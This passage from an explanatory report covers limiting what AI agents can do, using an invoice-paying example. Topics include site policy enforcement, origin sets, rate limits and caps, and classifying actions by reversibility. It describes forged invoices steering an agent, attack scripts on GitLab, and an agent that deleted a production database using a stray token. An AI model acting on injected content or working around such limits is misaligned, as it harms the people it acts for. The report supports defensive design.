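A language model chooses the policies for a task from a list that the site or another trusted source has written in advance. It sees the user's request and the descriptions of the policies, but no web pages, and the user confirms the choice. The three models tested chose the right policies for more than 94% of tasks in each category. They were less reliable on the 32 shopping tasks where they also had to fill in values such as spending limits, getting everything right on between 81% and 97% of them.

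Meng and colleagues then tested enforcement on GitLab with two ordinary tasks, commenting on an issue and upvoting it. To represent the worst case, they replaced the agent with 12 scripts, each carrying out a different attack, such as deleting a project or giving an attacker access. ceLLMate blocked all 12. Each attack required an action that the policy forbade, so the test confirms that the enforcement works but doesn't measure how much harm an attacker could do with permitted actions. An agent with permission to comment could still post something false or confidential.

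ceLLMate added a small delay. Eleven page loads took 13.93 seconds without it, 14.94 seconds with 100 entries in the sitemap and 16.02 seconds with 300, an increase of 7.25% to 15%. This would usually go unnoticed amid the model's own processing time.

Coverage is a bigger concern. Meng and colleagues wrote their map of 51 GitLab operations by hand, and someone has to update such a map whenever the site changes. They are right that a missing or incorrect entry leaves the user no worse off than before, but if the bank forgot to list its form for urgent payments, the company would think it had a limit that it didn't have. ceLLMate also doesn't check WebSockets, which many sites use for live updates, and it can't control desktop programs.

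### Limits on which sites an agent may use

Google's Chrome browser has a coarser control that requires nothing from websites. Parker (2025), in *Architecting Security for Agentic Capabilities in Chrome*, describes "origin sets", where an origin is roughly a site's address. For each task, Chrome keeps one set of origins that the agent may read and another where it may also click and type. A separate component decides which origins are relevant to the task, and it receives no untrusted web content that could manipulate its decisions.

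To pay invoice 2071, the agent might be allowed to read the accounting site and to read and act on the bank's site. A forged invoice could still influence what the agent does at the bank, but couldn't make it send the supplier list to an attacker's website. In the design, Chrome also keeps the model from reading embedded content that comes from unrelated origins, such as advertisements.

The control limits which sites the agent may act on, but not what it does there, so an agent allowed to act on the bank's site may press any button on it. Meng and colleagues rightly criticise the two modes as coarse. The first version was weaker than the full design because it tracked only the set of origins where the agent may act. Google Cloud has since told business customers about a similar control that limits the agent to origins relevant to the task. Neither account includes a measured rate of blocked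 attacks.

Chrome also asks the user to confirm some actions. Before the agent opens a banking or medical site, Chrome checks the address against a fixed list. Purchases, payments and messages are harder to detect, because Chrome has to infer from the page what a click will do. Parker says only that the agent "will try to pause" before these actions, and compares this safeguard to Google's other classifiers, whose accuracy the company is still improving.

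### Separate accounts for agents

The invoice company can avoid much of this inference by giving the agent its own login. If the bank allows several users, the company could set up a user that can prepare payments to existing payees but can't add a payee or release the money. The bookkeeper would release each payment with a separate login. The bank enforces these limits on its own servers, so they hold even if the agent clicks the wrong button or an attacker takes control of it.

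A separate login also solves the problem of traffic that looks human. The bank can set a lower limit for that user and, as with a separate API key, the company can trace the agent's payments and cut off only the agent. The agent also needs its own browser profile, without the bookkeeper's saved logins. Otherwise it could return to the bookkeeper's more powerful account, much as the PocketOS agent picked up a token from an unrelated file.

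This is probably the best first step for a company whose services support it. It doesn't help much where an account has only one login with full powers, as many personal accounts do. In that case, the browser could cryptographically sign an agent's requests, and the site could apply stricter limits to them than to the user's own. But the site would have to support the signatures, and an operator who wanted to avoid the limits could leave the signatures off. A restricted account limits even agents that don't cooperate.

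### Websites that declare their own tools

WebMCP is a proposed web standard that would let a page offer structured tools to a browser agent. According to documentation from Google (2026), a developer can define a tool in JavaScript or add labels to an existing form. Each tool has a name and an input schema, as in MCP. A bank could define a `send_payment` tool that takes an invoice, an account and an amount, and the agent could call it instead of working out what each form field is for. The tool runs visibly on the page, so the bookkeeper can still watch, and the bank can require confirmation.

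This would bring back the arguments that clicks leave out, so a policy like Progent's could check them again. But WebMCP doesn't remove the payment form. The page is still open in the bookkeeper's session, and an agent that can click can still fill in the form. To benefit fully, the company would have to let the agent call tools on the bank's site and prevent it from clicking there.

The website also writes the descriptions of its tools, so agents have the same reason to distrust them as they do hints from an MCP server. Chromium's *Intent to Experiment*, a notice from the open-source project behind Chrome, warns that a site may collect sensitive information when an agent calls its tools, and leaves agents to guard against this and prompt injection. It helps that content a page embeds from another origin, such as an advertisement, can't register tools unless the page allows it.

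WebMCP is still experimental. PPC Land, a trade publication, describes it as a draft from a community group of the World Wide Web Consortium, a web standards body. Chrome began a public trial with version 149. Chromium planned to continue the trial through version 156 and estimated a full release in version 157, but had no signal of support from the developers of Firefox's and Safari's engines. Microsoft's *WebMCP* page lists a trial that expires on 17 November 2026. In May, Google (2026) said that its agent, Gemini in Chrome, would support WebMCP soon. In early October, Google's documentation still described WebMCP as a proposed standard that could change.

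Meng and colleagues think websites are unlikely to offer MCP tools widely any time soon, and note that most sites took about two decades to adopt encrypted connections. WebMCP takes less work, particularly for sites that only need to label a form. But Google warns that developers of complex sites will probably have to restructure some of their code, and that an agent can't find out which tools a site has without visiting it.

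Zhang and colleagues describe wrapping a graphical program in an API, so that a call such as `GenerateReport(startDate, endDate)` operates the program's menus and dialog boxes. The company could do the same without waiting for its bank, by writing a fixed script that fills in the bank's payment form and offering it to the agent as `send_payment`. The script would hold the bank login, and the agent could supply only the invoice, account and amount. A redesign of the bank's website could break the script, so the script should stop if the page doesn't match the one it was written for.

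### Whether structured calls still get more done

Graphical agents used to lag far behind agents with APIs, so a company could choose structured calls for performance and get better control as a bonus. That gap has narrowed. Aggarwal and Welleck (2026), in *Computer-Use Agents Are Embodied Generalists*, compared the two interfaces on tasks from four research competitions. They built software for each competition, and ran the same model with the same operations through a screen and through a text API:

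| Task | API score | Graphical score |
|---|---|---|
| Navigating a 3D scene | 83.9 | 85.2 |
| Navigating with help from a guide | 67.4 | 63.4 |
| Marking parts of objects in 3D scans | 26.7 | 28.1 |
| Marking moving objects in videos | 95.8 | 94.6 |

The scores differ by four points at most, and each interface did better on two of the tasks. But these tasks are very different from paying invoices. They are highly visual, and the researchers designed the screens, whereas a bank's website has pop-ups, session timeouts and forms that nobody designed for an agent. The models also came from a single series, Google's Gemini Flash. Aggarwal and Welleck caution that efficiency may differ even where success doesn't, and six clicks generally take longer than one call.

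*GUI vs. CLI* tested agents on ordinary desktop software, and there too the best graphical agent did better than the best command-line agent, completing 59.1% of a matched set of tasks compared with 48.2%. But the command-line agents worked through predefined skills, and their success rate rose to 69.3% once the researchers added missing skills. Similarly, Bechard and colleagues found that roughly half of the listed tools' disadvantage with business software came from operations that nobody had provided.

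So control, more than success rates, is now the main reason to prefer structured calls. Zhu and Cai (2026), in *From Language Models to World-Acting Systems*, call APIs the most legible way for an agent to act, because the service can authenticate the caller, validate the arguments and record the request. An agent with a complete set of tools also finishes as many tasks as one that clicks, or nearly as many. That may not be true of an incomplete set, so the company shouldn't ban clicking before it has tools for the operations its agent needs.

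The company can divide the work according to what each step could damage. The agent could download invoices from supplier portals using a browser profile that has never been used to log in to the bank, and make payments only through `send_payment`. It might still try to pay a forged invoice, but the request to pay NEWBANK-8830 would be a tool call containing the account number, and the policy would reject it.

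## Rate limits and cumulative caps

The policy that rejects a payment to NEWBANK-8830 could still let the agent pay the paper supplier $1,200 twenty times. The software has to track earlier calls to stop the repeats. A rate limit restricts how many actions the agent can take in a given period, and a cumulative cap restricts the total money, records or recipients those actions affect. Both limit the harm the agent can do before someone notices, even if nobody knows which payment is wrong.

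### The token bucket

Network engineers often limit traffic with a token bucket. The tokens are only a count and have nothing to do with the access tokens that services issue. For the invoice agent, the bucket could have a capacity *B* of 5 payments and a refill rate *r* of 2 an hour:

1. The bucket starts full, with 5 tokens.
2. The software adds tokens at a steady 2 an hour and discards any beyond 5.
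3. When the agent proposes a payment and the bucket holds at least one token, the software removes one and lets the payment through.
4. If the bucket holds less than one token, the software blocks the payment and leaves the bucket as it is.

One day might go like this:

| Time | Payments proposed | Tokens before | Result | Tokens after |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| 9:00 | 5 | 5 | All pass | 0 |
| 9:15 | 1 | 0.5 | Blocked | 0.5 |
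| 9:30 | 1 | 1 | Passes | 0 |
| 11:00 | 2 | 3 | Both pass | 1 |
| 17:00 | 0 | 5 (full) | | 5 |

The agent can pay several bills that arrive together, but then it must slow to one every half hour. In any period of *T* hours, it can make at most *B* + *rT* payments, because each payment uses one token, the bucket holds at most *B* tokens at the start, and at most *rT* more arrive during the period. *Token Bucket Rate Limiting*, a textbook chapter on network traffic, proves the same bound for data passing through a router.

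The chapter lists three ways to treat traffic that exceeds the limit: delay it, drop it, or mark it for lower priority. Delaying payments is risky because queued payments could still go out after someone has stopped the agent. The company should either refuse payments over the limit or make sure that stopping the agent also empties the queue.

A simpler limit is the fixed-window counter, which counts actions in each clock hour and resets to zero when the next hour begins. With a limit of 5 an hour, the agent could make 5 payments at 9:59 and 5 more at 10:00, which is twice the limit in about a minute. A token bucket with a capacity of 5 would block nearly all of the second batch.

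The bucket can also let an agent exceed the hourly rate. With a refill rate of 2 an hour, the agent above could make 7 payments in its first hour. But the company can set the size of a burst separately from the long-run rate, whereas a fixed window uses one number for both. If the company wants an exact limit, it can store the time of every payment and count the payments made in the past sixty minutes. That takes little storage for an agent that pays a few dozen bills a week.

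### How much the company can lose

If each action can lose at most *v*, and someone stops the agent after *T* hours, then

largest loss = (*B* + *rT*) × *v*

Suppose the company lets the agent pay bills of up to $200 on its own and leaves larger ones to the bookkeeper. If the agent starts paying forged invoices at the beginning of an eight-hour day and the bookkeeper notices at the end, the agent can make 5 + 2 × 8 = 21 payments, so the company can lose up to $4,200.

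The formula also shows which settings matter most:

| Change to the illustration | Payments | Largest loss |
|---|---|---|
| None | 21 | $4,200 |
| Capacity of 1 instead of 5 | 17 | $3,400 |
| Refill rate of 1 an hour instead of 2 | 13 | $2,600 |
| Bookkeeper notices after 1 hour | 7 | $1,400 |
| Payments of up to $5,000 | 21 | $105,000 |

Adding a cumulative cap of $1,000 a day reduces the largest loss from $4,200 to $1,000, or five payments of $200. However, if the cap resets at midnight, an agent running from 8 p.m. to 4 a.m. can pay $1,000 before midnight and another $1,000 after. Applying the cap to any 24-hour period avoids this.

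The cap matters more the longer the agent runs unsupervised. In the 63 hours from 6 p.m. on Friday to 9 a.m. on Monday, the rate limit alone would allow 131 payments and a loss of $26,200. A cap of $1,000 in any 24 hours would limit the loss to $3,000.

These figures are based on every wrong payment being a total loss, which overstates the harm if the bank can recover some of the money. They could also understate it, because an attacker who stays below the cap may go unnoticed for much longer than a weekend. At $1,000 a day, a month of forged invoices would cost $30,000. A monthly cap would limit the loss, as would having someone compare the bank statement with the invoices every week.

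Caps also stop legitimate work. If $1,400 of small bills are due on the same day, some have to wait, and forged invoices that use up the allowance will delay the real ones. *Persistent Billable State* (Zhang, Xia and colleagues, 2026) describes the same trade-off for attacks that run up an agent's computing bill. A budget keeps the bill from growing indefinitely, but an attack can exhaust it and interrupt the task. For the invoice company, paying a bill late usually costs less than paying forged invoices without a limit.

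### What to count

A limit on calls is easy to build, but the number of calls may say little about the damage:

| Action | What to count | Reason |
|---|---|---|
| `send_payment` | Dollars, in total and for each supplier | One call can pay $1 or $5,000 |
| `send_email` | Recipients | One message can go to every supplier |
| `delete_record` | Calls | Each call deletes one entry |
| `list_invoices` | Records returned | One call can return every supplier's details |
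| Calls to the model | Computing cost | Later calls usually cost more than earlier ones |

Each token in a token bucket can represent a dollar instead of a payment, so a $200 payment removes 200 tokens. The company can also apply several limits to the same call and allow it only if it meets them all.

Later calls to a model usually cost more because the software sends the model much of the earlier conversation each time. Providers charge by the token, which for a language model is a short piece of text. Zhang, Xia and colleagues give a formula for the total input over *N* calls, where *P* is the length of the initial prompt and *D* (in place of their symbol) is the average length of what a tool returns:

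total input = *NP* + *D* × *N*(*N* − 1)/2

If each model call resends the prompt and all earlier tool results, a 1,000-token prompt with 500 tokens of results per call uses 32,500 input tokens over ten calls and 115,000 over twenty. Doubling the calls multiplies the input by about 3.5, so a limit on calls is a poor substitute for a limit on cost.

*Token Budgets* (Khan, 2026) compares five common ways of limiting an agent on a task in which it keeps retrying. Three of them limited the number of steps or turns, and in the worst case spending reached about fourteen times the intended cap. The other two tracked dollars but checked the total only after each call had returned, so they did not stop the call that exceeded the cap. Khan's own program calculates the most a call could cost and reserves that amount beforehand. On the main version of the task, with a cap of two cents, it never overspent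 in 30 runs, while the other five methods overspent every time.

Khan had set the model to give the same answers each time, so those 30 runs were nearly identical and are closer to one observation than to thirty. Another 160 runs with more varied answers also produced no overspending. For a single agent, though, a four-line Python counter that reserved the same amounts did just as well, so the benefit came from checking before the call.

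Reserving the maximum leaves some of the budget unused. In a live test with a cap of five cents, Khan's program refused 18 of 40 tasks although it had spent only about four cents. Payments don't have this problem because the request states the exact amount.

Khan also collected 63 confirmed reports of agents that overspent on computing, from 2023 to 2026. The largest loss was about $2,150, and one user of Claude Code spent $235 in four days. Khan searched for failures, so the collection can't show how common they are, but Khan found no case where anyone prevented the overrun before a user had paid for it.

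Other resources may need limits too. *Agent libOS* (2026) describes a system that sets budgets for resources including tool and model calls, bytes read from and written to files, processor time, and memory. The budgets are separate from permission, so having budget left never allows an agent to take an action that its policy forbids.

### Split payments, retries and parallel agents

If the agent misreads a $120 bill as $1,200, the $200 limit blocks the payment, but the agent could still try to send six payments of $200. The daily cap would stop the sixth. To stop the second payment, the company has to keep a running total of payments on each invoice and compare it with the amount owed.

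Retries are harder to count. Suppose the bank makes a payment but its confirmation never arrives. The agent sees an error and tries again, and a counter that records only confirmed payments misses the first payment. Like ToolFence, *Agent libOS* reserves part of the allowance before a call. If the outcome is unclear and it has no better measurement, it counts the whole reservation as used.

This protects the cap, but the supplier may still receive the money twice. An idempotency key, which is an identifier attached to a request, prevents that. A service that supports these keys performs the first request with a given key and returns the same result for any repeats. The key for invoice 2071 could be `pay-2071`. Software outside the model should attach it, because if the agent made up a new key for each attempt, the bank would treat every attempt as a new payment. If the company pays an invoice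 in instalments, each approved instalment needs its own key.

Where a service doesn't support such keys, the company has to find out what happened before it tries again. *Bounded Autonomy* (Chen, Lyu and colleagues, 2026) describes a system that does this, with all model and tool calls routed through one gateway. If an action didn't happen, the agent may retry it. If the action did happen, the system keeps the result. If nobody can establish the outcome, the system forbids a retry.

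Their system also gives retries a separate budget. Out of a total budget *H* of model tokens, it sets aside a fixed fraction *ρ* when the task begins:

recovery pool = *ρH*, rounded down

For example, if a task has a budget of 200,000 tokens and the fraction set aside for retries is 0.2, all its retries share 40,000 tokens. Nothing refills this pool, and renaming the agent or restarting a step doesn't reset the count of attempts. In tests with simulated attacks, the system completed between 59% and 81% of the interrupted steps that it allowed to resume, depending on the attack.

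When a limit applies to each agent separately, running more agents in parallel raises the total they can do. *Token Bucket Rate Limiting* notes that *N* senders with a bucket each can together send at *N* times the rate of one sender, with bursts *N* times as large. Three invoice agents with the settings above could together make 63 payments in eight hours and lose $12,600. They need a shared counter that adds every agent's payments to one company-wide total. For agents that start sub-agents, *Agent libOS* counts each action against the allowance of the agent that took it and of every agent above it in the chain, so starting more sub-agents doesn't increase the total allowance.

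A shared counter can still fail if agents check it and update it in separate steps. Khan demonstrated this with three agents that shared a budget of 60 units (each a thousandth of a cent) and made calls costing 23 units each. All three checked the budget before any had recorded its spending, so each found enough left. In all 30 trials, they spent 69 units in total. When each agent had to check the budget and reserve its amount in a single step, while the others were locked out, none of the 30 trials overspent.

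The locked version was also less productive. Each agent reserved 31 units to be safe, so only one could go ahead, although the budget would have covered the units that two calls actually use.

A shared counter works best at a point that every action must pass through. A counter in the agent's own software misses payments from other agents, and one at the company's gateway misses payments that an agent sends directly to the bank after finding the bank key. The bank processes all of these payments, and its limit should cover the whole account, including payments made on its website.

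### Circuit breakers

A circuit breaker stops the agent altogether when its activity looks wrong. It could stop the invoice agent after three identical payment requests, five errors in a row from the bank, or more payments in an hour than the company made in any hour last quarter. The agent should stay stopped until a person restarts it. A breaker reduces *T* in the loss formula because the company no longer depends on the bookkeeper to notice the problem. If the breaker cuts *T* from eight hours to half an hour, the largest loss in the illustration falls from $4,200 to $1,200.

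The breaker should distinguish permanent errors from temporary ones. If the bank reports that an account is closed, another attempt is pointless, but a timeout may resolve itself. AWS's *Tool integration and management practices*, guidance from Amazon's cloud business, warns against using one retry policy for every tool, because agents then keep calling services that have failed permanently and give up too soon on those with a brief fault.

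The gateway in Chen and colleagues' system stops ordinary work when it detects repeated errors, identical calls or a long stretch without progress. It uses fixed thresholds rather than a model's judgment. Together with the system's budgets, these stops reduced token use by 76.9% in the most extreme test, where an attacker made tools return enormous outputs. Against an attacker who caused repeated errors, the reduction was at most about 5%. That test injected no more than four errors per task, so there was probably little waste to prevent.

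The protected agent sometimes completed fewer tasks than the unprotected one. Under the heaviest version of an attack that filled the agent's context with useless text, the protected agent completed 43% of its tasks and the unprotected one 57%. Without attacks, the two performed about equally well.

Thresholds based on short tasks can be too strict for long ones. Zhang, Xia and colleagues found that no legitimate session in their main tests cost more than $0.025, while attacks cost as much as $3.40. A fixed cap of $0.10 would allow all of those legitimate sessions, but under that cap the agent completed only 13 of a separate set of 24 longer workflows. It completed 22 when the software authorised further spending as the work progressed.

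Extending an agent's computing limit when it makes progress is a sensible way to control computing costs, as long as the software judges progress from something other than the agent's own claims. Chen and colleagues check the state of the business application, such as its order records. Extending a payment cap in the same way would be a mistake, because paying a forged invoice also looks like progress.

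Few researchers have measured how well limits on agents work. The available tests, from 2025 and 2026, mainly cover computing costs, and comparable measurements for caps on payments, emails or deletions are hard to find. Some evidence also suggests that developers rarely build cost limits into MCP software. Zhang, Xia and colleagues found signs of a safeguard against runaway costs in only 71 of 3,830 public code repositories for MCP servers and connections. The true share of protected agents is likely higher, because a company may set its limits in a gateway or with its model provider, which a scan of public code would miss.

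### Limits on automated trading

Stock markets had to control fast automated actions long before language models could use tools. In 2010, the US Securities and Exchange Commission (SEC) adopted Rule 15c3-5, which applies to brokers that trade directly on an exchange or let customers trade through them. The SEC's *Risk Management Controls for Brokers or Dealers with Market Access* (2010) gives the example of a faulty program that places 1,000 orders a second, each for 300 shares at $20. If nobody notices for two minutes, it places 120,000 orders worth $720 million. This is the same calculation as *rT* × *v*, except that $720 million is the value of the orders, and the loss would probably be smaller.

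The SEC's market access rule requires brokers to block orders that would exceed a pre-set credit or capital threshold, or that appear to be mistakes, before they reach the exchange. For example, a broker's software could reject an order priced unreasonably far from the current market price. Surveillance staff must also receive immediate reports of completed trades, but the SEC considered controls that work only after the trade inadequate.

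The broker must also have direct and exclusive control of these checks, with limited exceptions. Some brokers had let customers send orders straight to an exchange and relied on the customers' assurances that they had suitable controls, which is much like relying on an instruction in an agent's prompt. Brokers must review their controls at least once a year, and the chief executive must certify that the controls comply.

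Most of this applies to the invoice agent. The company can set the cap in advance, check each payment against it, keep the counter where the agent can't change it, and review the settings regularly. Mistakes are harder to detect because invoices have no market price, so the company has to compare each one with its own orders and past bills. The SEC's document describes what the rule was meant to achieve, so it is a precedent for the design but not evidence of how many errors the rule has prevented. The SEC expected the technology to cost an average broker about $51,000 at first. A small company would spend far less if its bank already offers daily limits.

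### A single harmful call

A rate limit cannot stop the first call. Even if *B* is 1 and *r* is 0, the formula gives a loss of *v*, which is enormous for some actions. The PocketOS agent deleted the production database with one command, which a limit of one deletion a day would have allowed.

A cumulative cap can stop a single large action if the request includes the action's size. For example, the $1,000 cap blocks a $12,000 payment on the first attempt. But a request to delete a storage volume doesn't include the number of customer bookings on it. To protect the company from such a request, the cap would have to allow zero deletions, unless something else can delay or reverse the deletion.

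## Classifying actions by whether they can be undone

A limit of zero deletions makes sense for a storage volume that nobody can restore, but it would be needlessly strict for a ledger entry that the agent could restore in a second. To treat the two differently, the company has to work out which actions are reversible. Many actions can't be labeled simply "reversible" or "irreversible".

In *From Interaction to Impact*, Zhang, Schoop and colleagues (2025) studied the effects of smartphone actions and began with three labels: instantly reversible, reversible in several steps, and irreversible without outside help. The experts they consulted found these too simple. Some messaging apps let people retract a message for only two minutes. A customer can easily cancel an order just after placing it, but has to return the goods once they have shipped. Undoing an action can leave traces, such as the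 editing history of a shared document. Deleting a message also doesn't make the recipient forget any sensitive information it contained.

If the invoice agent schedules a payment for Friday, the company may be able to cancel it until Thursday night, but after that it has to ask the paper supplier for a refund. Whether an action can be undone also depends on who is trying to undo it, since PocketOS couldn't restore its deleted volume but Railway could.

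Researchers in automated planning changed their view of reversibility in a similar way. Under the classical definition, according to *POLAR* (Kang, Cho and colleagues, 2026), an action was reversible if some sequence of further actions could restore the starting state. Later work treated reversibility as a matter of degree.

### Five classes, from no effect to irreversible

Waghmare and Sufi (2026), in *Can You Undo It?*, sort tool calls into five classes and suggest a default policy for each:

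| Class | Name | What recovery involves | Suggested policy |
|---|---|---|---|
| R0 | No effect | Nothing outside the agent has changed | Act |
| R1 | Restorable | The agent can put the earlier state back exactly | Act, then notify someone |
| R2 | Compensable | A known further action leads to an acceptable equivalent at a limited, known cost | Ask, or use a budget approved in advance |
| R3 | Hard to recover | Recovery takes a person, an outside process or open-ended effort; the class also covers changes to access, credentials, availability or physical objects | Ask each time |
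| R4 | Irreversible | Nobody can recall the effect or make up for it | Act only with explicit authorisation |

R1 is the most demanding class to justify, because it lets the agent change something without asking. Waghmare and Sufi require three conditions for exact restoration:

1. A complete record of the earlier state exists, either in a version history or in a copy made before the action.
2. The principal can already write that state back without anyone else's help.
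3. No outside party has seen, received or acted on the changed state.

An audit log might meet only the first condition. For example, the invoice company's log may contain every detail of a deleted ledger entry, but that doesn't help the agent if only the bookkeeper can re-enter it.

When the agent deleted PocketOS's volume, Railway's documentation described such deletions as permanent, so PocketOS had good reason to treat the action as R4. With hindsight it was R3, because recovery was possible but depended on Railway. Railway's new 48-hour hold lets customers reverse a deletion, but it would make the deletion R1 only if the service kept running during the hold, because an outage changes availability and PocketOS's customers would notice it.

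### How arguments change the class

The name of a tool is rarely enough to determine its class. The invoice agent's calls might be classified like this:

| Call | Circumstances | Class |
|---|---|---|
| `list_invoices` | Any | R0 |
| `send_payment` to PAPER-4471, dated next Friday | The bank cancels scheduled payments for a $10 fee | R2 |
| `send_payment` to PAPER-4471, today | The supplier would have to agree to a refund | R3 |
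| `send_payment` to NEWBANK-8830, today | The recipient is a thief who won't return the money | R4 |
| `send_email` to a supplier | The supplier can read it at once | R4 |
| `delete_record` | The ledger keeps old versions, and the agent may restore them | R1 |
| `delete_record` | Only the bookkeeper can restore the entry | R3 |
| `delete_record` | No copy exists | R4 |

The two payments to the paper supplier differ only in date. The three deletions could be identical requests, so software can't distinguish them without information about how the company has set up its ledger.

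Waghmare and Sufi handle differences in arguments with ordered rules. Each tool has a base class that reflects the broadest effect it can have, and rules lower the class for calls of a narrower kind. For payments, the rules might be:

```
send_payment                                     base class R4
  if account is an approved supplier
     and date is at least 2 days away            R2
  if account is an approved supplier             R3
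```

The software applies the first rule that matches. If the company swapped the two rules, every payment to an approved supplier would be R3, because the software would never reach the rule about dates. As another fail-safe default, a call that matches neither rule stays at R4, and so does a call to a tool that nobody has classified.

A rule should lower an action's class only when the request matches a precise definition of a safe request. Checking only that a dangerous word is absent would fail for the same reasons as permitting every SQL query that begins with `SELECT`. A company can also override a class for its own systems if it records why, for example because its ledger saves a copy before each deletion. It can't lower the class of a disclosure this way, because the outsider would still know the information.

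The classes are also hardest to apply to disclosure. Waghmare and Sufi put deliberate delivery of content to outsiders in R4, but they ignore notifications that are only a side effect of an action. For example, if the bank automatically tells the paper supplier that a payment is scheduled, the payment stays in R2. The exception is sensible because so many actions notify somebody, but two careful people could easily disagree about which notifications are side effects.

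*Revisable by Design* (Zhai, Li and Wang, 2026) classifies email differently. It divides actions into those that change nothing, those with an exact inverse, those that can be compensated for, and those that can't. It treats a sent email as compensable because the agent can send a correction. It examines whether an agent can still satisfy a user who changes the instructions halfway through a task. A correction works if the agent told the paper supplier the wrong delivery date, but not if it sent the supplier a competitor's prices. R4 is the safer default for setting permissions, although it means treating the wrong date as seriously as the leak.

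Zhai and colleagues also calculate a task's reversibility ratio, the share of available tools that either change nothing or have an exact inverse. If the ledger keeps old versions, the invoice agent's ratio is 2/4, or 0.5. They conclude that, in a run of *n* actions, at least (1 − ratio) × *n* will be hard or impossible to undo. This holds only if the agent uses its tools about equally often. An agent that reads fifty invoices for every payment would take far fewer of these actions than the formula predicts.

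Kang and colleagues replace classes with a score between 0 and 1. An exact inverse scores *w*, a weight for how confident the person who wrote the entry is. An action that somebody can compensate for scores *w* × (1 − loss), and an irreversible action scores 0. A sequence of actions gets the score of its weakest step:

score of a sequence = min(score of each step)

If *w* is 1 and the loss weight for the $10 cancellation fee is 0.1, the scheduled payment scores 0.9. If the agent also emails the supplier, the score for the whole sequence falls to 0. Taking the minimum prevents harmless steps from offsetting an irreversible one, but it doesn't add up small losses. Twenty scheduled payments would still score 0.9, although cancelling them all would cost $200. A person chooses the weights, so the score can look more precise than it is.

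### Draft labels for 536 tools

Waghmare and Sufi have published a registry that assigns a class to each of 536 tools on 20 MCP servers:

| Class | Share of the registry | Number of tools |
|---|---|---|
| No effect (R0) | 62% | 333 |
| Restorable (R1) | 6% | 31 |
| Compensable (R2) | 3% | 18 |
| Hard to recover (R3) | 7% | 39 |
| Irreversible (R4) | 21% | 115 |

More than half of the tools that can change something are in R4. The share of agents' changes that are irreversible may differ, because agents use some tools more often than others and a tool whose broadest effect is R4 may have many calls in lower classes. The labels are drafts that Waghmare and Sufi prepared with AI assistance, so the table describes their current judgments.

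They used the registry to test how well MCP's hints indicate whether recovery is possible. They used the hints to class read-only tools as R0, other tools that deal with outside entities as R4, remaining destructive tools as R3, and all others as R1. These classes differed from the registry's for 118 of the 481 tools they could compare (24.5%). The hint-based class was higher for 85 tools and lower for 33.

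No combination of hints produces R2, so the hints put all 13 comparable R2 tools in other classes. The hints would also put every call to `send_payment` in R4, even when the company could cancel the payment for $10.

The disagreements matter less if a company only wants to know when to ask for approval. If it asks for approval for every tool in R2 or above, both methods give the same result for 57 of the 118 tools. For the other 61, using the hints instead of the registry would add an approval request for 41 and skip one for 20. Ten of those 20 are tools that the registry puts in R4 even though their hints describe them as read-only. These ten deserve attention first, but the comparison can't show which method is right because nobody has independently verified the registry.

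Waghmare and Sufi did have 150 of the labels reviewed, but the reviewer was Sufi. He gave the first nine ratings himself, one of them on an AI system's recommendation, and then approved AI-proposed ratings for another 139 tools in batches. For two Stripe tools, there was too little evidence to decide. Of the 148 ratings, 75 matched the registry:

| Registry label | Tools rated | Same class | Higher class | Lower class |
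|---|---|---|---|---|
| R0 | 34 | 28 | 6 | 0 |
| R1 | 31 | 1 | 30 | 0 |
| R2 | 16 | 5 | 11 | 0 |
| R3 | 33 | 11 | 20 | 2 |
| R4 | 34 | 30 | 0 | 4 |

The overall match of 50.7% understates the match across all tools, because the sample included every R1 and R2 tool but relatively few of the far more common R0 tools. Weighted by the size of each class, the match would be about 74%. The reviewer was a co-author and had seen the AI's suggestions, so neither figure measures accuracy or independent agreement. Some of those suggestions were wrong, including one that rated a browser search tool R0 even though the tool could write its results to a file.

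The most worrying result is for R1, where the review moved 30 of these 31 tools to a higher class. Under the suggested policy, an agent would then need approval or a budget to use any of the 30. Waghmare and Sufi attribute the differences partly to assumptions about who can carry out a recovery and whether outsiders have seen the change, which are two of the three conditions for R1. They also found a case in their own experiments where the documented undo for an R1 tool failed to restore everything. A company should therefore test whether an R1 label holds on its own systems.

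### How well people and models judge reversibility

Other evidence suggests that reversibility is unusually hard to judge. Zhang and colleagues at Apple and the University of Washington held four one-hour workshops with 12 experts in language models, AI safety and user interfaces. They asked the experts to imagine a voice assistant acting for them while their hands and eyes were busy, and to say which actions it should confirm with them before acting.

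The workshops produced a taxonomy of 10 general categories and 35 specific ones. It covers whether an action can be undone, what traces undoing it leaves, how it affects the user and other people, whether repeating it changes anything, and whether the user can tell that it worked. For example, if a phone app fails to turn off a garden's watering system, the owner may not find out until the water bill arrives.

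Existing collections of smartphone tasks mostly involved browsing and searching, so they were of little use for testing the taxonomy. The researchers instead asked 15 people to operate a remote phone through a web browser and find actions that they wouldn't want an agent to perform on its own. The participants used test accounts and chose from a list of 97 apps. They recorded 250 sequences of screens, and annotators removed the incomplete ones, leaving 209.

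Two annotators labelled each sequence, and a third settled disagreements. The annotators also rated each sequence's impact as minimal if an agent could safely act alone, moderate if they would want to confirm the action, and significant if they would want to take over. They rated 26.8% of sequences minimal, 49.3% moderate and 23.9% significant.

The first two annotators agreed on the level of impact 95.0% of the time, but on reversibility only 55.5% of the time. Part of this gap is because reversibility had five options and impact had three, and the percentages don't correct for chance agreement. The annotators also worked from screenshots, which often don't show how an app's undo works. People may know they want to confirm an action without knowing whether they could reverse it. If so, asking users to classify actions by reversibility is a poor way to decide when an agent should check with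 them.

Zhang and colleagues then tested five models, including two versions of GPT-4 and Gemini 1.5 Flash. The version of GPT-4 that could read images had the highest accuracy on impact, 58.37%, when given the taxonomy, worked examples and an instruction to reason step by step. It scored 25.84% without that help, and answering "moderate" every time would have scored about 49%. Accuracy on reversibility ranged from 46.56% to 67.13%, but the labels were uncertain because trained annotators often disagreed. The models also tended to exaggerate the impact of actions. GPT-4, for example, rated clearing an already empty calculator history as significant.

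Those models are long out of date, and so are most of the ones tested in *WebGuard* (Zheng, Liao and colleagues, 2025). *WebGuard* labelled 4,939 actions on 193 websites as safe, low-risk or high-risk, based on their consequences and reversibility. Without special training, no model reached 60% accuracy on average. OpenAI's o3 identified between 26% and 51% of high-risk actions, depending on the websites and the form of the input. Training a small open model on the labels raised its accuracy from 37% to 80% and the share of high-risk actions it identified from 20% to 76%.

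Some of the models' mistakes came from relying on an action's label instead of predicting its effect. For instance, models rated clicking a "Checkout" button as high-risk, although the button may only open the next page.

More recent tests show continuing problems, although none of them repeats the question about reversibility:

- In *OSGuard* (2026), Claude Sonnet 4.5 judged whether individual computer actions were safe. When it called an action unsafe it was right 77% of the time, but it caught only 48% of the unsafe actions.
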